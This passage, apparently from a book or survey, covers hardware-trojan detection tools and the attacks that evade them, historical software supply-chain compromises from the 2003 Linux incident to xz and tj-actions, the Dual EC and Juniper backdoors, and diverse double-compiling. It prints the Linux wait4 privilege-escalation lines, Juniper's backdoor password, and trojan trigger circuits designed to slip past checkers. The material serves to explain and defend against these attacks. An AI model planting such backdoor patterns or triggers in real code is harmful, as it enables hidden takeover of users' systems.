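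A fingerprint also needs a golden reference, here a set of chips known to be clean. Knechtel and colleagues point out that a customer who distrusts the foundry can't assume any of its chips are clean. One solution is to measure a few chips, then destroy them to check them against the layout. If they match, their measurements can serve as the fingerprint for the rest. This extends the microscope's result to chips that haven't been cut open, which helps against a foundry that alters only part of a batch. But if the inspection misses a lookalike swap in the samples, other chips with the same trojan will match the fingerprint.

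The researchers who ran the 2026 trial rank these checks by cost. They would start with secure handling of the layout file and a ban on lookalike cells, and would routinely run power measurements and functional tests, which are cheap. A trojan with a rare trigger can pass those tests, so they would add the microscope for chips that need more assurance.

### Automatic checkers for a chip's design

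None of these methods help if the trojan is already in the design. To find such trojans, researchers have built tools that search the hardware code or netlist for logic that appears to stay inactive until triggered. Each new tool led to attacks designed to avoid it.

#### Logic that the tests never use

Hicks, Finnicum and colleagues (2010), in *Overcoming an Untrusted Computing Base*, started from the observation that an attacker has to keep a trojan inactive during the designer's tests. Their method, unused circuit identification (UCI), flags logic that made no difference in any test. A coverage tool does something similar for lines of code, but they showed how an attacker can fool one. Suppose two control wires, c0 and c1, choose between a good value and an attack value:

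- X is the good value if c0 is 0, and the attack value otherwise.
- Y is the good value if c1 is 0, and the attack value otherwise.
- The output is X if c0 is 0, and Y otherwise.

| c0 | c1 | X | Y | Output |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | good | good | good |
| 0 | 1 | good | attack | good |
| 1 | 0 | attack | good | good |
| 1 | 1 | attack | attack | attack |

Tests that use only the first three rows run both branches of every line, so a coverage tool reports nothing unusual. UCI instead looks at pairs of wires where one depends on the other. In these tests, the output always equals the good value, so a plain wire could replace the logic between the two, and UCI flags that logic as suspicious.

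Some flagged logic will be harmless, because no set of tests uses every legitimate part of a chip. Hicks and colleagues removed all the flagged logic but added a circuit that interrupts the processor whenever it needs a removed part. Software then computes the same result in another way, for example by replacing an OR instruction with XOR and NAND instructions. Their system stopped all three attacks they tried and slowed the processor slightly.

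#### Two gates that defeat UCI

A year later, in *Defeating UCI*, Sturton, Hicks and colleagues (2011) searched for circuits that UCI would miss. Two of them, Hicks and King, had also worked on UCI. Their program went through every circuit of up to three gates with one or two normal inputs and two trigger inputs. It kept those that behaved normally unless both trigger inputs were 1 and in which no two dependent wires stayed equal throughout testing. The search assumed that the tests covered every input except the trigger.

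Two NAND gates are enough to meet these conditions. A NAND gate outputs 0 only when both its inputs are 1. The first gate combines the trigger inputs t0 and t1, and the second combines the result with a normal input i:

output = NAND(i, NAND(t0, t1))

The first gate outputs 1 unless both triggers are 1, and the circuit then outputs the opposite of i. When both triggers are 1, the circuit outputs 1 whatever i is. UCI looks for a wire that always equals another wire it depends on, and this circuit has none. In every test, the circuit's output is the opposite of i, and the first gate outputs 1, which doesn't always match either trigger because each is sometimes 0.

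Sturton and colleagues used one of the circuits from their search to put a backdoor in the Leon3, the processor that King and colleagues had attacked. A program that ran a secret sequence of instructions gained supervisor rights, and UCI did not flag the added logic. The attack worked even though the attacker could not choose the designer's tests. The researchers saw no easy repair, because a method that infers correct behavior only from tests cannot judge cases the tests leave out. They also thought that designers of future checkers would struggle to define a broad enough class of malicious circuits to look for.

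#### Inputs that hardly ever matter

FANCI, a tool that Waksman, Suozzo and Sethumadhavan introduced in 2013, doesn't use the designer's tests. It calculates how often each input to a piece of logic can affect the result. This fraction is the input's control value. For t0 in the two-gate circuit, there are four combinations of the other inputs to consider:

| i | t1 | Output if t0 = 0 | Output if t0 = 1 | Does t0 matter? |
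|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 1 | 1 | No |
| 0 | 1 | 1 | 1 | No |
| 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 | No |
| 1 | 1 | 0 | 1 | Yes |

The control value of t0 is 1/4, and that of i is 3/4. A value of 1/4 is common in unaltered circuits, but a trigger with only two inputs would often go off by accident. If the attacker uses 64 trigger inputs to make such accidents rare, the control value of each falls to 1/2^64, far below normal. The tool can't check every row of a table that large, so it estimates the values from a sample of rows.

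In 2013, research groups from several continents tried to get backdoors past FANCI. Waksman, Rajendran and colleagues report the results in *A Red Team/Blue Team Assessment of Functional Analysis Methods*. The attackers could create their own designs, so the defenders had no clean version to compare them with. The defenders had about three days in total and spent about an hour per design examining what FANCI flagged.

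FANCI detected every stealthy backdoor, including one that waited for a 66-bit code. It missed most of the backdoors that were often active. One of these switched on with the reset signal, and another worked during half of every clock cycle. Their triggers are not rare, so their control values look normal. Waksman and colleagues argue that ordinary tests should catch such backdoors, and that designers should use both checks together. An attacker who makes the trigger rarer to escape the tests makes the backdoor easier for FANCI to detect, and vice versa. The argument holds only if the tests cover the backdoor's behavior, and the contest entries exploited signals that testers tend to neglect.

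#### Triggers spread over several clock cycles

The contest also exposed a weakness in how FANCI handled registers. The tool usually stopped its analysis at a register and treated the stored value as a new input. A team from UT Tyler put registers between nearly all the complex gates in part of its design. The defenders could see immediately that something was wrong, but FANCI did not easily detect the backdoor.

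An attacker can use this to hide a 64-bit trigger by spreading the check over three clock cycles. The circuit first checks the bits in 16 groups of four and stores the 16 results. In the next cycle, it combines these into four results, and in the one after that into a single result. Each input to a four-input AND gate affects the output only when the other three are 1, so its control value is 1/8. The complete trigger is as rare as it would be with a single 64-bit check, but its gates look ordinary in FANCI's analysis.

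*DeTrust* (2014), by Zhang, Yuan and Xu, turned this into a general method. Their trojans evaded both FANCI and VeriTrust, another checker of the time, by spreading the trigger over several clock cycles and mixing it with the circuit's normal logic. The attackers knew how the tools measured suspicion, so they could adjust a trojan until its scores looked normal.

Waksman and colleagues had already proposed fixing this by treating registers as plain wires, so that the analysis could continue through them. In the three-cycle example, this would bring all 64 trigger inputs back into one calculation, and their tiny control values would reappear. But many circuits, such as counters, feed a register's output back into its own input, so following the wires leads around in a loop. The tool has to stop somewhere, and an attacker who knows where it stops can spread the trigger beyond that point.

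## Incidents in products and standards

In a detection trial, the organizers know where every change is, so they can count the ones the checkers missed. Nobody can do this for real attacks, because the public record includes only those that someone noticed. But the record does include information a trial can't provide, such as how long an attacker's change stayed in a product and how it was discovered.

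### An unapproved change to Linux

In 2003, the Linux developers kept the master copy of their source code in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them refused to use it, so a server also published an automatic copy in another system, CVS. Every change in the copy included a reference to the record of its approval. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) describes how, on November 5, Larry McVoy noticed a change without one. Nobody had approved the change, and it did not exist in the master copy. Someone had apparently broken into the CVS server and added two lines to `wait4`, a function that programs use to wait for an event:

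`if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))`
`retval = -EINVAL;`

The lines look like a check that returns an error for an unusual combination of options, but the single `=` sets the running program's user number to 0, the administrator's number, which gives the program full control of the machine. C then treats the stored 0 as false, so the error line never runs and the program continues. According to Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered*, the attacker had also put the name of David Miller, a long-time Linux developer, on the change.

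McVoy flagged the change before he understood it. Another developer, Chad Kitching, pointed out that the code looked like a backdoor. In *Re*, his reply on the developers' mailing list, McVoy (2003) said he had missed the single `=`. In *Re*, a later message in the same discussion, Szepe (2003) noted that the parentheses around the assignment would stop GCC from warning about it. A commenter at Freedom to Tinker objects that C requires parentheses there anyway. Either way, the warning that worked on some contest entries would probably not have appeared. A reader who knew the function had a better clue, because `wait4` has no reason to touch the user number, as InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) points out.

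The change lasted about a day, and Debian's *CVE-2003-1161* records that no released version of Linux contained it. The CVS copy never sent changes back to the master copy, so the attacker may have hoped that a developer would work from the altered copy and submit the two lines along with other changes.

The check that succeeded tested where the code came from, so it didn't depend on how well the attacker had disguised the code. The same check would not have helped against someone with permission to approve changes.

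### Infected development tools

Induc, a virus that infected the Delphi programming system, came closer to Thompson's attack. When an infected program started, it looked for Delphi versions 4 to 7 on the computer. If it found one, it copied the source of a standard library file, added the virus's code, compiled the result and deleted the altered source. From then on, every program the developer compiled contained the virus, even though the developer's source code was clean.

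Lipovský (2011) thought in *Win32/Induc.C* that Thompson's lecture had influenced Induc's design. Unlike Thompson's backdoor, though, Induc did not need to survive a rebuild of the compiler. It spread when somebody ran an infected program on another developer's computer. Reinstalling Delphi removed it from the tools, but developers then had to recompile their infected programs.

A bug in the virus made infected programs crash with "runtime error 3" on machines where Delphi's settings were damaged, for example after someone had uninstalled Delphi. Users asked about the error on a Russian forum, and a programmer called Aleksandr Alekseev traced it to the virus on August 12, 2009. Alekseev's *Check your Delphi's installation* (2009), published by EurekaLog, says that people noticed the virus only because of this bug.

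Securelist's *A short history of Induc*, from the antivirus company Kaspersky, says that the virus had been circulating for a year. The oldest infected files it mentions date from November or December 2008, which would be about nine months. During that time, infected programs passed several kinds of check:

- Antivirus programs look for harmful behavior, and the first version of Induc did nothing except copy itself.
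- Security companies had put infected programs on their lists of software known to be safe.
- The messaging program QIP compared itself with a stored checksum each time it started, but the checksum was calculated with the virus already inside. Removing the virus made the check fail.

When Alekseev sent a sample to Symantec, another antivirus company, it replied that the file contained no malicious code. Securelist even found Induc inside several Brazilian programs for stealing bank details, presumably because the criminals who wrote them had compiled them with infected copies of Delphi.

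Securelist doubted that criminals would adopt the method, since they had simpler ones and a harmful payload would attract attention. Two years later, a new version of Induc had a payload that downloaded other malware, including a password stealer, from addresses hidden in profile pictures on discussion forums.

In 2015, attackers spread the XcodeGhost malware through altered copies of Xcode, Apple's tool for building iPhone and Mac apps. The installer was nearly 3 gigabytes, and downloads from Apple could be very slow in China, so some developers got it elsewhere. The attackers put their copies on Baidu's file-sharing service and posted links on Chinese developer forums. Palo Alto Networks' *Novel Malware XcodeGhost Modifies Xcode, Infects Apple iOS Apps* reports that every copy of versions 6.1 to 6.4 that the company downloaded was infected.

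The attackers added a file of compiled code to Xcode without altering the compiler. The file's name resembled that of one of Apple's own libraries. They also changed a setting of the linker, the tool that joins compiled pieces into a finished program, so that it included the file in every app. Palo Alto Networks' *More Details on the XcodeGhost Malware and Affected iOS Apps* notes that this change did not appear in Xcode's windows but did appear in the build logs.

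Infected apps, including the messaging app WeChat, passed Apple's review and appeared in its App Store. They sent information about the device to the attackers' servers and could display messages or open links on command. Palo Alto Networks first reported that the code could steal passwords through a fake dialog, but later corrected this because the dialog had no text field.

Checking Xcode's digital signature would also have caught the altered copy before it built anything. Apple signs Xcode, and Antiy's *Analysis and Review of Xcode Unofficial Supply Chain Pollution Incident (XcodeGhost)* (2015) shows that the altered copy fails signature verification. The developers who used it had apparently not checked the signature.

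The earliest forum post Antiy found dates from March 16, 2015, six months before the first public warning in September. Tencent, which makes WeChat, discovered the attack. 21CTO's *What Was XcodeGhost?*, a later retelling, says Tencent's security team noticed an app sending encrypted traffic to a suspicious address when it opened and closed.

The scale became clear only years later, when a lawsuit made Apple's internal emails public. According to VICE's *The Fortnite Trial Is Exposing Details About the Biggest iPhone Hack*, 128 million customers had downloaded more than 2,500 affected apps. Apple said in 2015 that it had no information that anyone had used the malware to do harm.

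### Tampering during builds and releases

SolarWinds sells Orion, a program that companies and governments use to monitor their networks. In 2020, attackers added a backdoor called SUNBURST to it without leaving a lasting change in the company's source code. They used a program called SUNSPOT on the server that built Orion. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT*, which analyzes a copy from that server, describes how it worked:

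1. Once a second, it checked whether MsBuild.exe, Microsoft's build program, was running.
2. It read the build program's memory to see whether the product was Orion.
3. It compared checksums to make sure that the source file was the version it expected and that its own replacement was intact.
4. It saved the original file and put a version with the backdoor in its place.
5. When the build finished, it restored the original.

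A developer who opened the file before or after a build would have seen clean code. The attackers also turned off compiler warnings around their code, so nothing unusual appeared in the build log. They could signal SUNSPOT to finish its current swap before stopping, since a half-finished swap could have broken the build and started an investigation.

SolarWinds then signed the finished product and sent it out as an update (Krebs on Security, 2021). Checking the signature would have correctly shown a customer that the update came from SolarWinds, but not that the binary no longer matched the company's source code.

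The earliest suspicious activity SolarWinds found dates from September 2019. The attackers tested their method on an October 2019 release and began inserting the SUNBURST backdoor on February 20, 2020. According to SolarWinds, Orion releases from March to June contained it. The attackers removed their code from the company's systems in June, but customers who had installed the affected releases still had the backdoor.

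At least one customer, the US Justice Department, came close to finding the backdoor. Wired's *The Untold Story of the Boldest Supply-Chain Hack Ever* reports that a team working for the department suspected Orion and named a particular file to SolarWinds. The company's engineers looked for a vulnerability in their code and found none. The backdoor was not in the stored source code, so they could not have found it if they looked only there.

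In late November 2020, the security company FireEye investigated an alert that an employee had registered a second phone to receive login codes. Mandia (2021), FireEye's chief executive, says in his testimony to Congress, *Prepared Statement of Kevin Mandia*, that such alerts are common when new phones come out. But this employee had not registered the second phone. More than 100 people worked on the investigation, and after trying almost every other lead, they took apart the Orion binary and found the backdoor. FireEye told SolarWinds on December 12, almost ten months after the attackers had begun inserting it. By then, the attackers had broken into dozens of organizations.

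In the 2024 xz case, the attacker had permission to publish the software. xz is a set of file compression tools, and on some versions of Linux its library also runs inside the server for SSH, the usual way to log in to a machine remotely. The attacker, who used the name Jia Tan, had contributed to the project for about two years and become one of its maintainers. A check like the one that caught the Linux change would have found nothing wrong, because an authorized maintainer had made the changes.

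Jia Tan hid most of the backdoor in two of the project's compressed test files, which Patrakov lists by name in *Re* (2024). One was supposed to be a damaged archive for testing how xz handles errors, so a reviewer would expect its contents to make no sense. The instructions for extracting the hidden code and adding it to the library were only in the release tarballs, the packaged source files that Linux distributions download. As Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024) points out, someone who read the public repository would have seen nothing wrong. Anyone who built the software from a tarball got the backdoor, and rebuilding from the same tarball would have added it again.

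The two affected versions of xz came out in late February and on March 9. On March 29, the programmer Andres Freund reported the backdoor publicly in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024). He wrote that he had noticed errors from valgrind, a tool that looks for memory mistakes, and SSH logins that used a lot of processor time and took about half a second longer than usual. He first suspected that someone had tampered with the Debian package, then found that the problem came from xz itself. By then, the backdoor had been in released versions for about five weeks and had reached mainly test versions of Linux distributions.

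### Build services and packages since 2025

In March 2025, attackers altered tj-actions/changed-files, a small tool that more than 23,000 projects used in GitHub's automated build service. They redirected the tool's existing version labels to malicious code. Projects that used those labels then ran the code, which printed passwords and access keys into build logs that anyone could read if the project was public. The security company StepSecurity noticed within about a day, because its monitoring software recorded a network connection that the tool had never made before. Projects that identified the tool's code by its cryptographic hash instead of a version label did not receive the altered version.

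The Shai-Hulud worm appeared that September in npm, the main library of JavaScript packages. It stole the login details of a package's maintainer, then used them to publish infected versions of the maintainer's other packages. Malka and colleagues distinguish the worm from their tampered `strip` because each infected package contained malicious source code that a reviewer could read, and rebuilding from the original source removed the infection. Their October 2026 review of earlier attacks describes no real case in which a tampered tool infected its own later versions during builds from clean source.

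### Dual EC

In each of these cases, an attacker made a product work differently from how its users expected. Dual EC is a random number generator whose published specification may have contained a backdoor. NIST issued the specification in 2006, and the National Security Agency (NSA) had played a leading part in designing the generator.

The generator uses two published constants, P and Q, which are points on an elliptic curve. Such points can be added together, and sQ means the sum of s copies of Q. A computer can quickly calculate sQ from s and Q, but nobody knows a practical way to recover s from Q and sQ on a curve of this size.

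The generator's secret state is a number s. Leaving aside some details, each step calculates

output = x(sQ)
next state = x(sP),

where x( ) means the first coordinate of the point. Someone who sees only the output can't work out s, so the next state should stay secret.

Now suppose that whoever chose the constants knows a number d for which P = dQ. Such a number is easy to arrange by choosing it first and calculating one point from the other. That person can take the point sQ from the output and multiply it by d:

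d(sQ) = s(dQ) = sP.

The first coordinate of sP is the next state. From a single output, the person who knows d can therefore calculate every later one.

This example shows the arithmetic with ordinary numbers in place of points on the curve, keeping only the remainder after dividing by 101. Let Q = 7 and d = 5, so P = 5 × 7 = 35. If the state is 12, the output is 12 × 7 = 84, and the next state is 12 × 35 = 420, which leaves 16. An attacker who sees 84 and knows d can calculate 5 × 84 = 420 and also get 16. Anyone could find d by division here, but on the curve only someone who arranged the constants would know it.

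The real generator makes the attack slightly harder by leaving out 16 of the 256 bits of each output. The attacker has to try 65,536 possibilities for the missing bits, discard those that don't match a point on the curve, and compare the rest with the next output. A point and its mirror image share a first coordinate, but the attacker can use either one because both lead to the same next state.

Shumow and Ferguson, two Microsoft researchers, presented this attack at a cryptography conference in 2007. They could show that a suitable d existed but not that anyone knew it, and they stressed that they were not accusing NIST of planting a backdoor.

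Tests of products that used Dual EC could not have shown whether it had a backdoor. A conformance test checks that a product calculates the right outputs from the published P and Q. A product with the backdoor passes this test, because the attacker can exploit a faithful implementation of the specification.

Dual EC stayed in the standard for years after the 2007 talk. In September 2013, newspapers reported that documents leaked by Edward Snowden described NSA efforts to weaken encryption standards. NIST then advised people to stop using the generator and dropped it in 2014. Reuters reported in December 2013 that the NSA had paid the security company RSA $10 million in a deal that made Dual EC the default in one of RSA's products. RSA denied knowingly weakening its products. No one has publicly shown that they know d for the published constants, so the backdoor remains a strong suspicion.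 In 2014, Checkoway and colleagues had to substitute their own Q to measure how practical the attack was against encrypted web connections.

#### A second attacker at Juniper

In 2008, the network company Juniper began using Dual EC in ScreenOS, the software in its NetScreen firewalls. It chose its own Q instead of the published one. Juniper said the firewalls passed Dual EC's output through a second generator, which would have hidden the values an attacker needs.

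*A Systematic Analysis of the Juniper Dual EC Incident* (Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues, 2016) showed that the second generator in the firewalls' software never ran. Two routines shared a loop counter, and the first left it at a value that made the second one's loop end before it started. The firewalls therefore sent out raw Dual EC output. It is unclear whether this was deliberate or accidental, which is the kind of deniability that the Underhanded C Contest rewarded.

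In 2012, an intruder replaced the constant Q in Juniper's random number generator. Anyone who knew the matching secret value d could then record a customer's encrypted connections and decrypt them. The intruder did not need to add any code, because the generator and the faulty loop were already there. The new 256-bit constant would have looked as random to a reviewer as the original.

Juniper announced the problem in December 2015, after finding unauthorized code during an internal review. The altered constant had been in place for about three years. Juniper also found a second backdoor in the review, a password that worked for any administrator account. The password was `<<< %s(un='%s') = %u`, which looks like code for printing debugging messages.

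### Constants from a public rule

Designers can make this kind of backdoor much harder to plant by deriving their constants from a rule that anyone can check. The hash function SHA-256, for example, starts from eight constants, which are the first 32 bits of the fractional parts of the square roots of the first eight prime numbers. This rule left the designers almost no freedom to choose values with a hidden property.

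For Dual EC, a designer could have hashed a public phrase and used the result as the first coordinate of Q, adding a counter to the phrase until the result matched a point on the curve. The designer could then have found d only by solving the same problem that protects the generator from everyone else. The rule prevents the backdoor because the backdoor depends on choosing d first and calculating a constant from it. Under the rule, any reviewer who recalculated Q would also have discovered the switch at Juniper.

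A public rule still leaves some freedom, because someone has to choose the rule. Bernstein, Chou and colleagues explored this for elliptic curves in *How to Manipulate Curve Standards* (2014). By varying the starting constant, the hash function and other plausible details, they could produce over a million curves, each with a respectable explanation. A designer who secretly knew how to break one curve in a million could keep trying rules until one produced a weak curve.

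The same trick would be of little use with Dual EC, because trying a million phrases would give a million different values of Q and the designer wouldn't know d for any of them. A public rule therefore helps more when harmful values are rare. It also helps more when the designer has to commit to the rule before seeing the results.

### Disputed hardware cases

In 2012, Skorobogatov and Woods reported a backdoor in the ProASIC3, an Actel FPGA with military uses. Customers can lock the chip so that nobody can read out the design they have loaded. The researchers searched the chip's test connection for undocumented commands and found some that required a secret key, which they recovered from tiny variations in the chip's power use. According to their paper, *Breakthrough Silicon Scanning Discovers Backdoor in Military Chip*, the key gave access to functions that could bypass the customer's lock.

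The paper presented no evidence that China was responsible, though some early news coverage blamed it. Microsemi, which had bought Actel, denied designing any feature to bypass customers' security. It said the chip had an internal test facility for use in the factory, and that this was disabled in the chips it shipped. Other security researchers also thought a leftover test function was the most likely explanation. Microsemi disputed the paper's account of what the commands could do and why they existed, but in both accounts they were part of Actel's own design, so the case is not evidence of tampering at a foundry.

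Bloomberg Businessweek's *The Big Hack* (2018) reported that Chinese agents had added a chip the size of a grain of rice to server circuit boards made for the American company Supermicro, and that the boards had reached almost 30 companies, including Apple and Amazon. Apple, Amazon and Supermicro denied it in detail. The US Department of Homeland Security and Britain's National Cyber Security Centre said they had no reason to doubt the denials. An outside firm hired by Supermicro tested boards and found no malicious hardware. Bloomberg stood by its reporting and published a further article in 2021, but nobody has publicly produced an altered board. If the story were true, the tampering would have happened during board assembly, after the foundry had finished its work.

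There is better evidence of tampering in transit, which doesn't require redesigning a chip. An NSA document that Glenn Greenwald published in 2014 describes the agency intercepting shipments of network equipment, installing implants and sending the equipment on to its buyers.

As of late 2026, no malicious trojan added at a chip foundry appears to have been publicly confirmed. Sisejkovic and colleagues knew of none in 2023, and neither disputed case would be an example even if the accusations were correct.

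### How far the known cases can be trusted as a sample

| Case | Time before exposure | What exposed it |
|---|---|---|
| Linux, 2003 | About a day | A missing approval reference |
| Induc | About nine months | Crashes caused by a bug in the virus |
| XcodeGhost | Six months | Unexpected network traffic from an app |
| SolarWinds | Almost ten months | A login alert at a customer |
| xz | About five weeks | Slow logins and memory errors |
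| Juniper's altered constant | About three years | An internal code review |
| tj-actions | About a day | Software that monitors builds |

Checks intended to catch unauthorized changes worked in three of these seven cases (Linux, Juniper and tj-actions). In the other four, someone noticed a side effect and was curious enough to investigate. The attackers could have avoided several of those side effects. If Induc's author had handled damaged settings properly, or if the xz backdoor had run faster, those attacks might have lasted much longer.

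Attacks without such mistakes are less likely to appear in the table. Suppose that attackers plant 100 backdoors, of which 50 are clumsy and 50 are careful. Each year, people discover 40% of the remaining clumsy ones and 2% of the remaining careful ones. After three years, they will have found about 39 clumsy backdoors and 3 careful ones. Someone who studied only these 42 known cases would conclude that 93% of backdoors are clumsy, when the true figure is 50%. The times in the table have the same bias because they include only discovered attacks.

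These cases show that altered build tools have reached millions of people and that signed products can contain code their makers never wrote. They can't show how many backdoors remain undiscovered or how often code review succeeds, because nobody counts the attempts that reviewers reject.

No case in the table used the full version of Thompson's attack, which fits Cox's remark that attackers usually have much easier options. XcodeGhost needed a few forum posts and a fast download, and Shai-Hulud needed stolen login details. But a successful Thompson attack would also be harder to find than any of these, so some may have gone undetected. Cox's explanation is more plausible for ordinary criminals, who have little reason to put extra work into secrecy. It is less convincing for a patient intelligence agency, given that someone spent about two years becoming a maintainer of xz.

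The absence of confirmed foundry trojans is weaker evidence still. Freund could investigate a slow login on his own computer, and FireEye could reverse-engineer a binary it already had. A chip's owner would have to destroy it to check for a small change, and would also need the layout, which the manufacturer normally keeps secret.

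## Checking a compiler with a second compiler

A user who suspects a compiler has a backdoor could compare its binary with a clean one, as Cox could in his emulator, but usually the user has only the suspect binary and source code that looks innocent. David A. Wheeler's method, diverse double-compiling (DDC), uses an unrelated second compiler to work out, bit for bit, what the clean binary should be.

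Henry Spencer, inspired by an older exercise for finding compiler bugs, posted the idea in a few sentences in 1998. In 2004, people on a GCC mailing list knew of nobody who was doing it, and one wrote, "I guess we all sorta hope someone else is doing it." Wheeler named the method diverse double-compiling and presented the first public demonstration at a security conference in 2005. He extended this work in his 2009 dissertation, *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*.

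### Two compilations and a comparison

Suppose a user has a compiler's binary, A, and the source code s from which the supplier claims to have built it. The user also has a second compiler, T, which comes from somewhere else and can compile s. Let c(s, X) stand for the binary that compiler X produces from s. If A is a self-compiling compiler, the user takes four steps:

1. Compile s with A and check that the result is identical to A.
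2. Compile s with T to get a first build, B₁ = c(s, T).
3. Compile s with B₁ to get a second build, B₂ = c(s, B₁).
4. Compare B₂ with A, bit for bit.

Step 1 is a control. If it fails, the user has probably not reproduced the supplier's settings, and the later comparison would fail too. Many compiler projects already run a similar test to catch bugs. Passing it doesn't rule out a backdoor, because a compiler like Thompson's also reproduces itself exactly.

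DDC doesn't require two different compilers to produce the same binary, though Wheeler has often had to answer the objection that they never do. B₁ and A will normally differ, because T may choose other instructions, arrange memory differently, or even produce code for another type of processor. But if A is a faithful translation of s, it should behave the same way as B₁, which is also a translation of s. Both are compilers, so when the user compiles s with each of them, using the same settings, they should produce the same binary. A produces A, as step 1 confirmed, and B₁ produces B₂.

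Two C compilers will translate a program that prints the sum of 2 and 2 into different binaries, but both print 4. In diverse double-compiling (DDC), the program is itself a compiler, and its output is the next binary.

The second compilation reduces the comparison to checking whether two files are identical. Without it, the user would have to decide whether two different binaries, B₁ and A, always behave alike, and no general method can decide that for every pair of programs.

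Some suppliers build a compiler with an older version of it or with a different compiler, called its parent. The user then also needs the parent's source. The user compiles that source with T, uses the resulting compiler to compile s, and compares the output with A. The 2005 paper covered only compilers that compile themselves, and the dissertation extended the method to the general case.

Even a user who trusts T has reasons not to use it for everything. T may be slow, expensive or able to compile little besides s. More importantly, a backdoor in T would then go unchecked. With DDC, an attacker has to tamper with both compilers in the same way.

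### The procedure applied to Thompson's compiler

Thompson's compiler is a good test case. Cox reports that the clean binary is 10,724 bytes and the tampered one is 12,918. Suppose the user also has a second C compiler that can build the clean source.

| Suspect, A | Second compiler, T | Size of A | Size of B₂ | Comparison |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean | Clean | 10,724 | 10,724 | Match |
| Backdoor | Clean | 12,918 | 10,724 | Mismatch |
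| Clean | Backdoor | 10,724 | 12,918 | Mismatch |
| Backdoor | Same backdoor | 12,918 | 12,918 | Match |

If only the suspect compiler has been tampered with, T translates the clean source faithfully. B₁ then contains no backdoor and adds none to B₂, so B₂ is the clean binary the user was missing. The user can then look for the backdoor in the extra 2,194 bytes in A.

The third row assumes that T contains code to recognize the source of A. T inserts the backdoor into B₁, and B₁ inserts it into B₂. The comparison fails even though A is clean, so the user can't determine from a mismatch alone which compiler has the backdoor. Repeating the procedure with a different second compiler would help, because a B₂ of 10,724 bytes would indicate that the backdoor came from T. If T's backdoor recognizes only T's own source, it has no effect here, and B₂ matches A as it should.

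DDC fails in the case shown in the fourth row. The attacker has to make T recognize the source of A and give B₁ exactly the same backdoor as A. A different backdoor in T would lead to a different B₂, and the comparison would expose the tampering. The attacker also has to do this before the user picks T, and the user can pick at any time, keep the choice secret, or write a new compiler for the purpose.

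### What the proof establishes

Wheeler stated the argument in formal logic, had a theorem-proving program find the proofs, and had another program check each step. Let p be the source of the parent compiler. For a self-compiling compiler, p and s are the same. The main theorem is that if B₂ and A are identical, A does exactly what s specifies, with nothing added, left out or changed. It follows in four steps:

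1. T translates p accurately, so B₁ does what p specifies.
2. p specifies a compiler that translates s accurately, so B₁ translates s accurately.
3. B₁ produced B₂ from s, so B₂ does what s specifies.
4. A is identical to B₂, so A does what s specifies.

None of these steps requires compilation to be deterministic, meaning that the same input always gives the same output. Determinism matters for a second theorem, which covers the honest case. If the supplier built A from s with the parent, the parent's binary matches p, and a few other conditions hold, then A and B₂ must be identical. Without this result, a match would still be convincing, but honest compilers might never produce one. The theorem also implies that if A and B₂ differ, at least one of its assumptions is false, though the mismatch doesn't show which.

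#### Deterministic compilation

A compiler can break this assumption by recording the time in its output, choosing between optimizations at random, or sorting items by their memory addresses. Only the parent has to be deterministic, and only when it compiles s. T can produce different output each time, as long as it is always a correct translation. The parent's source must also not rely on anything the programming language leaves unspecified, because two correct compilers may handle it differently.

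#### A second compiler without the matching attack

Wheeler calls T the "trusted" compiler, but it only has to translate one program, p, correctly. It may be slow, be full of bugs that don't affect p, or even maliciously miscompile other programs.

A user can rarely prove that T meets this condition, though a compiler with a mathematical proof of correctness would be a good candidate. Wheeler usually relies on diversity instead. He prefers a T that shares no code with A and was never compiled by any version of A, since A could have inserted malicious code into it. An old compiler is useful because its developers could hardly have prepared a trigger for a program that didn't exist yet, provided the copy really is old. The user can also run T on a different operating system and processor, or change the source in ways that preserve its meaning, such as renaming variables, so that it no longer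 activates a trigger.

#### An honest comparison

The program that compares the files has to report the result correctly, and it must read the same A that people run. A tampered operating system could show a clean file to any program that reads A but run a different file when someone starts A. Wheeler suggests shutting the machine down and reading its disk from another system. He also recommends publishing cryptographic hashes (short fingerprints) of the source and binary with every successful result, because the result applies only to those exact files.

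The theorem's conclusion is certain only if its assumptions are true, and some of them are claims about particular machines and suppliers. Wheeler therefore compares a successful test to a legal proof rather than a mathematical one. Each further test with a different second compiler adds evidence.

### Trials on three compilers

#### TinyCC

For the 2005 demonstration, Wheeler chose TinyCC, a small C compiler by Fabrice Bellard. He built version 0.9.22 himself through a chain of earlier versions, so he had good reason to think the binary was clean. He used GCC as the second compiler. The first comparison failed anyway, and he eventually traced the failure to two ordinary defects.

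The first involved small numbers. Instructions for x86 processors can store a number from −128 to 127 in one byte instead of four. TinyCC checks whether a number fits by cutting it down to one byte and seeing whether its value has changed. TinyCC compiled this check incorrectly, so a copy of TinyCC compiled with TinyCC used four bytes for some negative numbers that needed only one. GCC compiled the check correctly, so some instructions took six bytes in one binary and three in the other. Both forms do the same thing, so a user would not have noticed the difference. TinyCC's list of known problems already mentioned the bug, but Wheeler found the entry only after tracking the problem down.

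The other defect affected how TinyCC stored zero in one numeric format. It reserved 12 bytes but set only 10, so the last two kept whatever was already in memory. The GCC-built copy wrote 11 zero bytes followed by a stray value, while the self-compiled copy wrote 12 zero bytes.

Wheeler changed a few lines of the source to avoid both problems, and the binaries then matched exactly. He could extend the result to the unmodified version by compiling its source with the compiler he had checked, since the difference between the two sources was small enough to inspect by eye.

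This trial was a weak security check because GCC had also compiled the first TinyCC in Wheeler's chain. A backdoor in GCC aimed at TinyCC could therefore have reached both sides of the comparison. The trial did show that the method is sensitive, since two unset bytes were enough to make the comparison fail.

#### A Lisp compiler with a known backdoor

The dissertation added a test on a compiler known to be malicious. Wolfgang Goerigk had written a small correct compiler for a version of the language Lisp, and a tampered one that carried out a trusting-trust attack. Both produced identical code for a factorial program, and both reproduced themselves from the correct source. But when they compiled a dummy `login` program that only returned the message "This is the correct login", the tampered compiler changed "correct" to "incorrect".

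Wheeler adapted the compilers to a more widely used version of Lisp and used an existing Lisp system, GNU Clisp, as his second compiler. B₂ was identical to the correct binary but not to the tampered one, which was 269 lines longer in printed form. The extra lines included a copy of the source of `login` and an instruction to compare incoming programs with it. Wheeler points out that there is no legitimate reason for a compiler to check for a particular login program.

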